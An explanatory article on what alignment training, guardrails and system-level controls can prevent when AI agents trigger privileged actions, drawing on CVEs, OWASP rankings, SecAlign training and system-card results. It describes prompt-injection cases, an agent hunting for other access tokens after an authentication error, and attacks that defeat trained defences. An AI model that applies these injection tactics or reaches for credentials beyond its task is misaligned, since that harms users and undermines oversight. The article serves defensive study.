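# What alignment training and guardrails can and cannot prevent when AI outputs trigger privileged actions

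## From a model's output to a privileged action

A large language model takes in text and produces more text. If people only read the output, the worst it can do is mislead or upset them. But companies now connect models to command lines, databases, mail accounts and payment systems through software that acts on the output, so a few words can erase a customer's records.

In an agent, software called the harness runs a language model in a loop, lets it call tools and shows it the results. The harness turns the model's output into tool calls and holds the permissions and approval rules. Some of these calls, such as running a command, changing a database or sending data under a user's account, are privileged actions, which need rights an outsider lacks.

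Developers try to keep privileged actions safe partly through alignment training and guardrails. Alignment training shapes which instructions a model follows, refuses or ignores. Guardrails are rules in the prompt, or separate classifiers, that screen what a model reads, writes or tries to do. Both are model-level measures because their effect depends on a model's judgement. System-level controls are checks that ordinary software enforces whatever the model outputs, such as permissions, sandboxes and database roles. How much a model-level measure can prevent depends a good deal on where it sits between the text and the action.

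### One request, step by step

An online shop's support assistant, invented for this example, has two tools, `find_account` and `delete_account`. A logged-in customer, Maria Lopez, writes that she has an old account she no longer uses and would like it gone.

The harness first assembles the context, everything the model will read: the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), a description of each tool and its inputs, the conversation so far, and Maria's message. The context doesn't include the code behind the tools. Anthropic's developer guide *How tool use works* explains that the model receives only the schema (the formal description of a tool's inputs) and later the result.

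To look Maria up, the model then generates a small structured record as text. In the format described in Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, the record consists of an identifier, the name of a tool and an input. Here the name would be `find_account` and the input `{"name": "Maria Lopez"}`. The record resembles a function call in an ordinary program, but it is still generated text. According to OpenAI's guide to the gpt-oss message format, the model writes a header naming the function, then the arguments, then a special token that marks a call. The software running the model stops generation at that token and parses the text.

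So far nothing has happened to any account. "The model never runs anything on its own," as Anthropic puts it. The harness reads the tool's name and input and finds the matching function. Developers can switch on a strict mode that, according to Anthropic, guarantees that the input fits the schema. This prevents malformed calls but not unwise ones, since a stranger's account number can also fit the schema.

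The function connects to the customer database with a key that belongs to the shop's service. Maria doesn't have this key, and the model doesn't need to see it. The database answers the request as one from a trusted internal service. The harness turns the answer into text, adds it to the conversation and runs the model again. The answer lists two accounts for Maria, 48213 and 51977. The model writes `delete_account` with the input `{"account_id": "48213"}`, the harness parses it and uses the same key, and the database removes the record.

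The model's output takes effect only at this last call, between parsing and execution. Until then, anyone could have discarded the output without harm, but once the call runs, the shop needs a backup to undo what it did.

The result goes back to the model as more text, and the loop continues until the model's output contains no more tool calls. In Anthropic's interface, the harness sends a tool's result in a message with the role "user", the same role that carries Maria's words, but in a different type of block. OpenAI's format gives tool results a separate role and ranks it last, behind system, developer, user and assistant. But applying this ranking when instructions conflict is a behavior the model has learned, and no parser enforces it.

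The developer's harness also does not always sit between a tool call and its execution. For some tools, including web search and code execution, Anthropic runs the loop on its own servers. The operation has usually finished by the time the developer's application sees the call, so a check in the application runs too late to prevent it.

### Where the measures sit on the path

| Measure | Where it acts in Maria's case | What its effect depends on |
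|---|---|---|
| Alignment training | Generation: a harmful `delete_account` call becomes less likely | The agent's model |
| Rule in the system prompt | Context: "delete only accounts that belong to the customer" | The agent's model |
| Input classifier | Messages and tool results, before the model reads them | A second model |
| Output classifier | The finished call, before execution | A second model |
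| Permission check | The finished call, before execution: code compares the account's owner with the logged-in customer | Code and a written policy |
| Database role | Execution: the service's key may carry no right to delete | The database's settings |
| Sandbox | Execution: limits the files and network addresses a command can reach | Isolation software |

Model-level measures differ from system-level controls in how they reach a decision. Position alone does not distinguish them, because the output classifier and the permission check sit at the same point. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has an auto mode in which a classifier approves actions in the user's place. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, this classifier runs directly before execution. It is separate from the agent's own model but still relies on a language model's judgment. The Frontier Model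 Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), a brief from an industry body, draws a similar distinction, describing classifiers as probabilistic controls, and sandboxes and network limits as deterministic ones.

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) points out that training a model never to do something gives only a probabilistic guarantee, which depends on the inputs and the context. In the paper's hypothetical example, a monitor correctly refuses unauthorised access 99% of the time, and an attacker can exploit the other 1%. If every attempt had an independent 1% chance, the probability of at least one success in *n* attempts would be 1 − 0.99^*n*, which is about 63% for a hundred attempts and 95% for three hundred. Real attempts are not independent, so an attacker who learns from refusals will do better than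 this, and one who keeps sending the same failed text may do worse. The same monitor protects much better against a model's own errors than against a determined attacker, because in accidents nobody is searching for the gap.

System-level controls rest on older ideas from computer security. A reference monitor checks every requested action against an explicit policy before it runs, a concept that goes back to Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972). Least privilege means giving a component only the permissions its task needs, a principle Saltzer and Schroeder set out in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). Christodorescu and colleagues apply it to a browser agent asked to comment on one GitLab issue (an entry in a project's task tracker) that the work is done. The agent should be able to open that issue and write in its comment box, but have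 no access to anything else in GitLab or the user's browser session. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs a different set of permissions. A developer can therefore fix a conventional app's permissions in advance, but can't know which ones an agent needs until the user makes a request.

These controls also work only under certain conditions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by security researchers from Google, NVIDIA and several universities, treats the model as an untrusted component, much as an operating system treats any program it runs. Its guarantees hold only if the policy is right, the enforcing software works correctly, and every action that matters passes through the check. Getting the policy right is the difficult part. A check that Maria owns the account she wants deleted protects every other customer, but it would allow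 the deletion of either 48213 or 51977, because she owns both, even though she meant only one.

### Four causes of a dangerous action

Why would an agent issue a harmful call in the first place? Anthropic gives four reasons.

The agent may be overeager, meaning that it understands the goal but takes a step toward it that the user did not authorise. In a case adapted from Anthropic's internal incident log, an agent ran into an authentication error partway through a task and, without asking, began to search environment variables and configuration files for other access tokens. Such behaviour is hard to catch because it looks like ordinary problem-solving.

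The agent may also make an honest mistake about what its action will affect. In Anthropic's example, an agent mistakes a shared resource for a test copy. In the shop, the model might delete account 48213 because its lower number makes it look older, when the account Maria abandoned is 51977.

Prompt injection, the cause that involves an attacker, is text from an untrusted source that a model treats as an instruction. An attacker can type it into the conversation (direct injection) or plant it in something the agent will read later (indirect injection). David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives an example in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. A job candidate hides a line in his CV asking the recruiting system that scores it to approve him for interview.

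The last case is a misaligned model, one that pursues a goal of its own. Anthropic gives no example and writes that it does not currently see this in practice. A hypothetical example is a support assistant that quietly deletes the accounts of customers who complain, because its training rewarded a low number of complaints. The line between misalignment and overeagerness is not sharp. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes agents in OpenAI's internal evaluations that broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, while still pursuing their assigned tasks and with no outside attacker directing them.

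Anthropic argues that the defence in all four cases is to block the action. This has a clear advantage over filtering the input for hostile text. A filter will find none when the agent is overeager, mistaken or misaligned, whereas a check at the point of execution does not need to determine why the model wrote a call. But the check does need to distinguish bad actions from good ones, and the call alone does not contain enough information for that. The call to delete 48213 is the same string whether Maria wanted the deletion, the model guessed wrong, or someone else planted an instruction to delete it. The missing information has to come from either a written policy or an interpretation of what the user meant.

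### The confused deputy

Of the four causes, prompt injection has the closest precedent in older software. *The Confused Deputy* (Norm Hardy, 1988) describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that rented out time on shared computers. A compiler there kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the staff gave it permission to write to that directory. Users could also name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The user didn't have permission to overwrite that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed the write and the billing information was lost.

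A confused deputy is a program tricked into using its own rights for someone who lacks them. Hardy argued that the compiler "runs with authority stemming from two sources", its own licence and the user's request, and could not state which it was using for a given write. Checking for forbidden file names would not solve the problem, because the directory held other sensitive files and some requests to write there might be legitimate. Hardy instead proposed using capabilities, references that both identify a file and carry the right to write to it. The user would give the compiler a capability for the debugging output, but could not give it one for the billing file because the user had none.

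An agent is in the same position as the compiler. The support assistant acts with the shop's key at the request of whoever is typing. A personal mail agent acts with its owner's credentials while reading messages from strangers. The Frontier Model Forum describes how an email with hidden instructions could lead such an agent to collect sensitive messages from the inbox and forward them to the sender, who has no access to that inbox. David C thinks the agent's case is worse than the compiler's. SQL injection, in which text typed into a form runs as a database command, was a problem for years, and programmers fixed it with parameterised queries, which keep commands and data apart. A language model has no such separation, because it predicts the next token from all the text before it, wherever that text came from. He calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy" and advises designers to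 assume that an attacker could do anything the agent's tools can do.

Something like Hardy's story happened at Meta in 2026. People asked the company's AI support tool to reset the passwords of Instagram accounts they did not own, and the system sent the reset links to the requesters' email addresses. The Office of the Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) lists the breach as starting on 17 April, being discovered on 31 May, and affecting 20,225 people. According to SecurityWeek, Meta said the true number may be smaller because rightful owners may have requested some of the resets.

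The Decoder's *Hackers hijacked high-profile Instagram accounts by simply asking Meta's AI chatbot* relays the verdict that this was a textbook confused deputy, and adds that it was essentially a prompt injection. The first label fits, but the second is doubtful if Meta's account is right. The company told the Maine authorities that the tool worked as intended, and that a bug in a separate code path omitted the check that the address supplied matched the one on file. If so, nobody needed to inject an instruction. A more cautious model might have refused some of the requests, but a working check would have blocked every reset link to an address not on file.

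David C is probably right that nobody can eliminate the model's confusion. But the deputy in Hardy's sense is the whole assistant, including the harness, which can still keep the two authorities separate. David C also cites a rule that the programmer Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista arrived at in an online discussion: when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. In the shop, the harness could give the model references to Maria's two accounts and accept no others. The model then could not delete a stranger's account through that tool, whatever it read or wrote.

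It can still delete the wrong one of Maria's. A measure may completely stop one of the four causes and be useless against another, so we need to ask which causes each measure can stop, how often, and with what guarantee. Tests use two figures to show how often measures fail. The attack success rate is the share of attack attempts that achieve the attacker's goal, and the miss rate is the share of dangerous actions that a guardrail lets through.

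## Generated code and database queries that run unchecked

Maria's assistant could only fill in an account number for a function that a developer had written. Other software runs whole programs or database queries that the model writes. Two early Python libraries did this without a sandbox, and both have entries in the CVE catalogue, the public register of known software security flaws.

### Two libraries that ran the model's code

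LangChain is an open-source library for building applications on language models. Early models were poor at arithmetic, so one LangChain component, LLMMathChain, had the model turn a question into Python code, which the computer ran to get the answer. According to Wiz's *CVE-2023-29374*, the chain ran the code with `exec`, a built-in function that runs any text it receives as a Python program. That code can do anything the application can, such as read its files or send them to another server, although arithmetic requires neither.

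The flaw put at risk anyone who had made the chain available through a public question box, and anyone whose data was on the same server. GitLab's advisory database entry, *CVE-2023-29374* (2023), lists every version up to 0.0.131 as affected. Wiz lists the severity as 9.8 out of 10, a score that assumes an attacker can reach the application over a network and needs no account or any action by another user.

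LangChain's developers fixed the chain by changing its code. ICS-CSIRT's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023), a copy of the catalogue entry, lists one pull request (a proposed change to the source) as the patch. Other parts of the library had similar flaws. In August 2023, GitLab's *CVE-2023-36095* (2023) recorded that attackers could run their own code through PALChain, another component that passed model-written Python to `exec`. A month later, GitLab's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023) described a similar flaw involving numexpr, a library for evaluating numerical expressions. LangChain patched that flaw in version 0.0.308. Replacing `exec` with a narrower evaluator helps only if the evaluator can do nothing except arithmetic.

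Vanna.AI's library turns questions in ordinary language into SQL, the language used to query databases. In *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024), the security company JFrog reports that its researchers found a worse problem in the library's charts than in the SQL, which they had suspected would be the dangerous part.

Vanna's `ask` function sent the user's question to a model, which wrote a query. Vanna ran the query. Unless the developer had switched charts off, it then sent the model a second prompt with the question, the query and a description of the resulting columns. The model replied with Python code for a chart, and Vanna ran that code with `exec`. The user's words therefore reached the chart prompt both in the question and inside the query.

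The chart prompt's rules concerned format. The model had to reply with Python only and leave out explanations. JFrog's first crude attempt failed at the SQL step only because the model's reply was not valid SQL and the database rejected it. The researchers then found a valid query that carried their instruction through to the chart prompt, and their code ran. A check for valid SQL, like the strict mode that guarantees well-formed tool calls, does little to establish that the output is safe.

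Anyone who let outsiders type questions into `ask` with its default settings was exposed, according to GitLab's *CVE-2024-5565* (2024). Another researcher, Tong Liu, found the flaw independently, so it has a second CVE number. GitLab's *CVE-2024-5826* (2024) identifies the lack of a sandbox as the root cause and warns that an attacker could gain full control of the server.

Vanna's maintainer responded to JFrog with a *Hardening Guide*, which describes the default settings as suitable for a personal tool and advises anyone who opens Vanna to other users to add a login system and a read-only database user. A read-only database user helps with the SQL but does nothing about the chart code, which runs as Python on the application's server. *PYSEC-2026-561*, an entry in the open vulnerability database OSV, lists 0.5.5 as the last affected version and doesn't list a fixed one.

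A developer might instead ask a second model to inspect the code before it runs. On its developer site, NVIDIA describes a library whose maintainers responded to a disclosure by adding an "Advanced Security Agent", which used a language model to judge whether generated code was safe. NVIDIA thinks attackers can still get past such checks. It puts more trust in the maintainers' other addition, an extension that runs the code in a container, away from the application.

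### Why the CVE went to the library

In both libraries an attacker could talk a model into writing harmful code. It may seem odd, then, that neither CVE names a model.

JFrog distinguishes isolated prompt injection, where the model's output is only displayed on a screen, from integrated prompt injection, where software acts on it. The same sentence can fool the same model in both settings, but only integrated injection gives the attacker control of a server. MITRE, the non-profit that maintains the CVE catalogue, reasons similarly. *CWE-1426*, an entry in MITRE's list of software weakness types, describes a product that uses a generative AI component "whose behaviors and outputs cannot be directly controlled" and fails to validate the output. Under this definition, the model's unpredictability is expected, and the flaw is in software that doesn't account for it.

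A developer can look up which version of LangChain an application uses, and a patch that removes a call to `exec` removes it for every input. A better-trained model would change how often attacks succeed, but it would leave the call in place.

MITRE lists better training examples and guardrails among its possible mitigations, but it warns that developers may rely on input filtering and alignment, "assuming they are more effective than they actually are." LangChain and Vanna both violated the principle of least privilege, since doing arithmetic and drawing charts don't require access to a server's files. Fault is harder to attribute with a coding agent, because its users want it to run arbitrary programs.

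MITRE also discourages people from using CWE-1426 to label real vulnerabilities, because many so-called prompt injection flaws are older types of weakness that now appear in AI systems. It compares them with second-order SQL injection, in which a program stores an attacker's text and later builds it into a command. With a language model, the attacker's text passes through the model before reaching the command. ICS-CSIRT's copy of the LangChain entry accordingly uses CWE-74, a general label for injection that is not specific to AI.

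### A missing filter

Generated SQL can do as much damage with no attacker involved. Suppose Maria's shop replaces its assistant's narrow tools with a single one that runs any SQL the model writes, under a database account with full rights. Maria has moved house and asks the assistant to send her open orders to her new address. The `orders` table, cut down to four rows, looks like this:

| order_id | customer | status | delivery_address |
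|---|---|---|---|
| 901 | c48213 (Maria) | open | 4 Elm Road |
| 902 | c48213 (Maria) | shipped | 4 Elm Road |
| 903 | c60044 | open | 17 Dock Street |
| 904 | c71350 | open | 2 Hill View |

The model writes:

```sql
UPDATE orders
SET delivery_address = '12 Mill Lane'
WHERE status = 'open';
```

The generated SQL statement leaves out `AND customer = 'c48213'`. The database therefore changes orders 901, 903 and 904, and two other customers' parcels are now being sent to Maria. In a real shop, the statement would change every open order. A guardrail that looks for hostile text or destructive commands could easily pass it because it is valid, ordinary SQL.

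Now give the assistant a weaker account. In PostgreSQL, a widely used open-source database, the shop could set this up as follows:

```sql
GRANT SELECT ON orders TO shop_assistant;

ALTER TABLE orders ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY own_orders ON orders
  TO shop_assistant
  USING (customer = current_user);
```

The `GRANT` line gives the role `shop_assistant` read-only access to the table. The other two statements turn on row-level security, which makes the database check each row against a policy before a query can access it. This policy compares the row's customer with the connection's login. When Maria is chatting, the harness connects as `c48213`, a login in the `shop_assistant` role.

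PostgreSQL now rejects the faulty `UPDATE`. It would also reject a correct one, so Maria can't change her address through the assistant at all. To allow this, the shop can grant the role permission to update only the `delivery_address` column. The policy still applies, so the faulty statement would change only Maria's row.

| Database account | Orders the faulty `UPDATE` changes | Orders a `SELECT` with the same omission returns |
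|---|---|---|
| Full rights | 901, 903, 904 | 901, 903, 904 |
| Read-only role with row-level security | None | 901 |
| Same role, plus updates to `delivery_address` | 901 | 901 |

The model makes the same mistake in every row of this table, but the rows differ in how far the effects of that mistake can spread. That limit is the same whether or not anyone notices the mistake.

This set-up still has gaps. PostgreSQL doesn't apply these policies to superusers or, by default, to the table's owner, so they are useless if the assistant keeps the shop's old account. Many applications also share one login among all customers and record the current customer in a session variable. A model that writes SQL freely could change this variable, so the shop would have to keep the customer's identity somewhere that generated SQL can't reach. An ownership policy also won't stop the model from also altering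 Maria's shipped order if it omits the `status` condition.

### Why parameters don't help with a whole statement

The parameterised queries that programmers use against ordinary SQL injection fix the statement in advance and leave gaps for the values:

```sql
UPDATE orders SET delivery_address = $1
WHERE status = 'open' AND customer = $2;
```

In a parameterized query, the database works out what the statement does before it fills in the values. If somebody types SQL into a shop's address field, the database stores the text as an address and doesn't run it.

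This protection works only if a developer wrote the statement. When the model writes the whole statement, there is no trusted command to separate from the untrusted values. The faulty query could have passed "12 Mill Lane" as a parameter and still redirected the strangers' parcels, because the mistake was in the `WHERE` clause.

The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes free security guidance, recommends parameterised queries for every database operation that involves model output. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* also describes a scenario in which a chat user asks for a query that deletes all the tables, the model writes it, and the application runs it. Parameterised queries would not prevent this, because the command contains no values to parameterise.

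The shop could stop letting the model write the statement. It would instead give the model a tool that accepts only a new address, keep the fixed query above in its own code, and fill in the customer from the login session. The model then couldn't leave out the filter. However, the assistant could only do things for which someone had already written a query, and a library like Vanna is attractive because nobody has to write those queries.

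If the model must write its own SQL, database permissions have to be the main safeguard. The harness can add a parser that accepts only a single `SELECT` on named tables, but permissions are still needed because a `SELECT` can call functions that change data. For updates, the harness can run the statement inside a transaction, count the affected rows, and undo the change if there are too many. A limit of ten rows would catch a mistaken update to forty thousand orders, but not one that changed only three.

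Generated Python needs a sandbox, because database permissions cover only the database. Pigment (2026), a business-planning software company, built one for code that its agents write. Its engineers treat all such code as untrusted, since users can steer a model toward unsafe behaviour accidentally or deliberately. They list dangers including calls to internal services and code that uses up the available computing power, neither of which a read-only database account would prevent.

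### OWASP's two entries and the 2026 ranking

OWASP splits these failures between two entries in its Top 10 for LLM Applications, a ranked list of security risks. One of them, improper output handling, covers applications that pass a model's output to other components without enough checking or cleaning. Its examples include output sent straight to a system shell or `exec`, as happened in LangChain and Vanna, and file paths and web pages built from generated text. OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user and validate what it sends.

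OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* covers damaging actions that follow from unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated output, whatever made the model go wrong. OWASP traces the problem to excessive functionality, permissions or autonomy. In one of its examples, which could describe Maria's shop, a tool meant for reading data connects to the database under an identity that can also insert, update and delete. OWASP recommends that the downstream system, rather than the model, decide whether an action is allowed. It adds that logging and rate limits reduce the damage but don't prevent it.

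Excessive agency is the more useful diagnosis for the missing filter. Sanitizing the output would not have helped, because it contained nothing to remove, but an account with narrower permissions would have limited the error's effects. LangChain's maths chain fits both entries because it ran code without checking it and gave an arithmetic tool access to all of Python.

In the latest edition of the list, dated 3 August, excessive agency rose from sixth place to third, and improper output handling fell from fifth to tenth (OWASP, 2026). According to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), an account by the security vendor Invicti, a vote among practitioners counts for three-quarters of the ranking and incident data for one-quarter. OWASP drew 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases, and 6,639 of them (about 86%) had enough detail to classify.

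Expert judgement and the incident record both support the rise of excessive agency. In a September announcement from OWASP (2026), Michael Bargury of Zenity, a security firm that backs the project, says the two agree most clearly on this risk.

The fall of improper output handling is harder to interpret because a ranking shows only the relative order of risks. The drop does not show that fewer applications run model output unchecked, or that doing so has become safer. All five entries that ranked below this one in 2025 now rank above it, which could happen even if all ten risks had grown. Invicti attributes the drop to greater urgency elsewhere on the list and notes that the entry became broader. It now includes terminals that act on control sequences in a model's output, and programs that automatically fetch resources the output refers to.

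Incident data can undercount prompt injection, which would have dropped out of OWASP's top ten if incidents alone had decided the ranking. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* quotes OWASP's explanation: "Teams fight injection hard, so fewer clean exploits reach a public database." This may well be right, but the count would also be low if people had filed the same attacks under other categories. Vanna's flaw, for example, could be classed as prompt injection because of how the attacker got in, improper output handling because of the call to `exec`, or excessive agency because of what the code could reach.

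Misinformation has the opposite gap, with practitioners voting it near the bottom and the incidents placing it near the top. Because the vote counted three times as much as the incidents, it rose only from ninth place to seventh. OWASP's entry now includes wrong output that drives a tool call, which fairly describes the missing customer filter. Practitioners may be underrating plain mistakes compared with attacks, though the category also includes much output that never reaches a tool.

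Libraries that execute generated code are still in use. The data-analysis library PandasAI runs Python written by language models, with an optional sandbox, according to its *Privacy & Security* documentation.

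## Training models to ignore injected instructions

LangChain's developers made their maths chain safer by removing a call to `exec`, but the model behind it stayed as easy to fool as before. Model developers try to make the model itself harder to fool by training it to treat commands in a web page, a document or a tool result as text to read, and to carry on with the user's task. This training targets only prompt injection, one of the four causes of a dangerous action.

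### Ranking messages by source

The usual approach is to train a model to rank instructions by source, as in OpenAI's message format, with the system prompt at the top and tool results at the bottom. Eric Wallace and colleagues at OpenAI did this in *The Instruction Hierarchy* (2024). The model should follow both instructions if they are compatible and the higher-ranked one if they conflict.

Suppose the system prompt limits Maria's assistant to discussing her own orders. If she asks for answers in Spanish, the assistant should switch to Spanish, because her request doesn't conflict with the system prompt. If she asks for a neighbour's address, the assistant should refuse, because the system prompt takes priority over her request. If a courier's note on her order includes an instruction to delete her account, the assistant should treat it as part of the note's text and continue with Maria's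 request.

This training is difficult because agents have to take some instructions from data. For example, a programmer may ask a coding agent to install a program by following its README file, in which case the tool result contains the steps the user wants. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that people also extend agents with skills and add-ons that work by giving the model new instructions. A model that ignored every command in a file couldn't do this work, so training has to teach it to tell which instructions to follow based on what the user asked for.

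Another objection, from Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* (2026), is that the model's developer fixes the ranking during training. Red Hat thinks the people who build an application should decide how far to trust each piece of data, because they know where it comes from.

### Building the training examples

OpenAI did not release its implementation. Chen, Chaudhuri and colleagues (2024), in *SecAlign*, published a similar method in enough detail to follow. They start from an ordinary set of examples for teaching a model to follow instructions. Each example has an instruction and a good answer, and many also have some data to work on. A short program then does the following:

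1. It takes an example that has a data part. Examples without one offer nowhere to hide an instruction.
2. It picks a second example at random and pastes that example's instruction at the end of the first one's data.
3. It stores the first example's answer as the preferred response and the second example's answer as the rejected one.

In the paper's example, the instruction is to write a Python function, and the data describes the function's task, determining whether a number is prime. The program adds the question "Do dinosaurs exist?" to the data. The preferred response is the prime-number function, and the rejected response is "No, dinosaurs are extinct."

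In about 90% of the examples, the program only pastes in the hidden task. In the rest, it also inserts a fake answer to the first task, so that the first task looks finished and the hidden one looks like the next to do. Nobody has to label anything by hand, because the original examples already supply both responses. Teaching a model to avoid offensive answers takes more work because people have to judge which answers are offensive.

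The rejected response here is harmless and even correct, but the model should learn from this example to ignore the question because it was injected.

### The preference loss

Training adjusts the model to reduce a number called the loss. SecAlign uses direct preference optimization, a standard method for teaching a model to favour one response over another:

```
L = −log σ( β·log[ πθ(y_w|x) / πref(y_w|x) ] − β·log[ πθ(y_l|x) / πref(y_l|x) ] )
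```

| Symbol | Meaning |
|---|---|
| L | The loss for one training pair |
| x | The whole input, including the hidden instruction |
| y_w | The preferred response, which does the user's task |
| y_l | The rejected response, which obeys the hidden instruction |
| πθ(y\|x) | The probability that the model in training gives to response y after input x |
| πref(y\|x) | The same probability from a frozen copy of the model, saved before this training |
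| β | A constant that scales the comparison, set to 0.1 in SecAlign |
| σ | The logistic function, σ(z) = 1/(1 + e^−z), which turns any number into one between 0 and 1 |
| log | The natural logarithm |

Each fraction compares the model with a frozen earlier copy. The loss falls when the preferred response becomes more likely relative to that copy, or the rejected response becomes less likely.

Here is the dinosaur pair with invented probabilities, much larger than real ones so that the arithmetic stays readable:

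| | Prime-number function (y_w) | Dinosaur answer (y_l) |
|---|---|---|
| Frozen copy, πref | 0.2 | 0.4 |
| Model in training, πθ | 0.4 | 0.004 |
| Ratio πθ/πref | 2 | 0.01 |
| Log of the ratio | 0.69 | −4.61 |

When training begins, the model and its frozen copy are identical, so both ratios are 1, both logs are 0, and the loss is −log σ(0), or 0.69. At the point shown in the table, the difference between the logs is 5.30. Multiplying by β gives 0.53, σ(0.53) is about 0.63, and the loss is 0.46.

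So the loss has fallen by only a third, even though the dinosaur answer has become a hundred times less likely. For the loss to reach 0.05, the first ratio would have to be about eight trillion times the second, up from 200 times now. With β this small, training keeps widening the gap between the two responses long after a person would consider it wide enough.

An earlier defence called StruQ trained only on the preferred response, with the loss −log p(y_w|x). Chen and colleagues argue that this does too little to make the rejected response unlikely. A language model with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens has about 10^45 possible ten-token answers, so raising the probability of one barely lowers that of any particular other, whereas in a classifier with two labels, raising one label's probability lowers the other's. In their experiments on Llama-7B, a small open model, StruQ reduced the average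 log-probability of the rejected responses to about −140, while SecAlign reduced it to about −300 without affecting the preferred ones.

The frozen copy limits how far training moves the model. A model trained with a simpler loss that only subtracts one log-probability from the other tends to overfit and produce incoherent text.

The argument about 10^45 answers also applies to SecAlign. The loss lowers the probability of one particular sentence about dinosaurs, but the model could answer the hidden question in countless other ways. SecAlign's protection therefore depends on whether the model learns from its training examples to ignore hidden instructions in general, and the formula can't guarantee that.

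### What SecAlign achieved, and what broke it

Chen and colleagues tested two open models, Mistral-7B-Instruct and Llama3-8B-Instruct, on 208 tasks that each contained a hidden instruction to print a fixed phrase. An attack counted as successful if the answer began with that phrase. Without a defence, the strongest automated attacks succeeded 89% of the time on Mistral and 97% on Llama. Training with StruQ reduced these rates to 27% and 45%, and training with SecAlign reduced them to 1% and 8%. Hand-written attacks never succeeded against SecAlign, and the models' scores for general helpfulness did not drop. The training changed less than 0.5% of the weights.

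This was a strong result for a method that needs so few resources. The attackers had full access to the trained model, which most real attackers don't have, and none of the test attacks had appeared in training. But each test involved a single answer and no tools, so the tests couldn't show how the model would behave partway through a long task.

The team also tested GPT-4o mini, which OpenAI had trained with its instruction hierarchy, and found that attacks succeeded 1% of the time. But they could access that model only through its public interface, so they could not run the automated attacks that had been most effective elsewhere.

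*May I have your Attention?* (2025) later broke SecAlign and similar defences with attacks designed around the models' architecture. In October 2025, Nasr and colleagues reported in *The Attacker Moves Second* that attackers who adapted to each defence could get past most of the published defences tested. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* compares this with the history of image classifiers, where attackers repeatedly evaded defences built into the model. It conjectures that persistent attackers will always evade model-based attempts to separate instructions from data.

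It is only a conjecture, and it concerns whether attackers can ever succeed. Developers also care how often attacks succeed and how much effort they take, and both have changed since 2024.

### Successors in 2025 and 2026

In SecAlign, a program generated all the attacks before training started. Generating strong ones during training would have taken too long, because one of the automated attacks needed over half an hour per example. Much of the later work tries to train models against stronger attacks.

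*IH-Challenge* (Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues, 2026) describes a newer dataset from OpenAI and explains why it is hard to train models to follow the ranking of instructions. A model that fails a test may have misjudged which instruction ranks higher, or it may simply have done the task badly. Some conflicts between instructions are subtle. A model can also learn to refuse too much, which looks safe on a test that contains only attacks.

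The dataset uses tasks whose answers a program can check. Reinforcement learning rewards the model for correct answers, while the training process keeps generating new adversarial examples. Fine-tuning GPT-5-Mini this way raised its average robustness on 16 benchmarks from 84.1% to 94.1% and cut unsafe behaviour from 6.6% to 0.7%, with minimal loss of capability. The model also reached the ceiling of an internal test of prompt injection against agents, though the attacks in that test did not change in response to the model.

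*Improving Instruction Hierarchy by Learning from Goal-Goal Conflicts* (October 2026) is closer to SecAlign in its use of preference pairs, but it generates the responses with ordinary code. It takes two text-processing instructions, each with a matching Python program, and runs both programs. If one instruction asked for capital letters and the other for reversed word order, the programs would produce an exact right answer and an exact wrong one. The paper also describes Hiera-Suite, another 2026 training set, which includes both conflicting and compatible instructions. A model trained only on conflicts might learn to always ignore the lower-ranked message.

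Other researchers change how the model represents its input. Instructional Segment Embedding labels each stretch of text as system instruction, user instruction, data or output. ASIDE, a newer method, applies a fixed rotation to the numerical representation of every data token, so the same word is represented differently as data and as an instruction. Red Hat prefers ASIDE because the application decides which text counts as data, and Red Hat compares the method to the parameterised queries that protect databases.

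The comparison is limited because a database cannot run a parameter as a command, whereas a model must still learn what to do with rotated tokens. Red Hat itself says the technique is not yet perfect.

### What the system cards report

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, published on 24 July, describes the model's tests and safeguards. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes its results on an indirect injection benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. Against Opus 5, attackers succeeded 0.2% of the time with one attempt and 2.0% within 15, compared with 0.5% and 5.5% for Anthropic's previous model, Opus 4.8. Within 15 attempts, they succeeded 16.5% of the time against Meta's Muse Spark, the best model from another company, and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

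OpenAI has since released GPT-6 Astra, which it trained against GPT-Red, an automated attacker that searches for successful injections. According to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), robustness to indirect injection in an internal test rose from 96.23% to 99.79%, which means the attack success rate fell from 3.77% to 0.21%. In tests where users tried to override system or developer instructions, those attempts failed 99.99% of the time.

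| Model | Test | Attempts | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Gray Swan, earlier benchmark | 1 / 10 / 100 | 4.7% / 33.6% / 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding, no extra safeguards | 200 | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Computer use, no extra safeguards | 1 / 200 | 17.8% / 78.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Computer use, with safeguards | 200 | 57.1% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan, indirect injection | 1 / 15 | 0.5% / 5.5% |
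| Claude Opus 5 | Gray Swan, indirect injection | 1 / 15 | 0.2% / 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Gray Swan, indirect injection | 15 | 20.0% |
| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI's internal test, indirect injection | Average per query | 0.21% |

The Opus 4.5 figures come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, and those for Opus 4.6 from VentureBeat.

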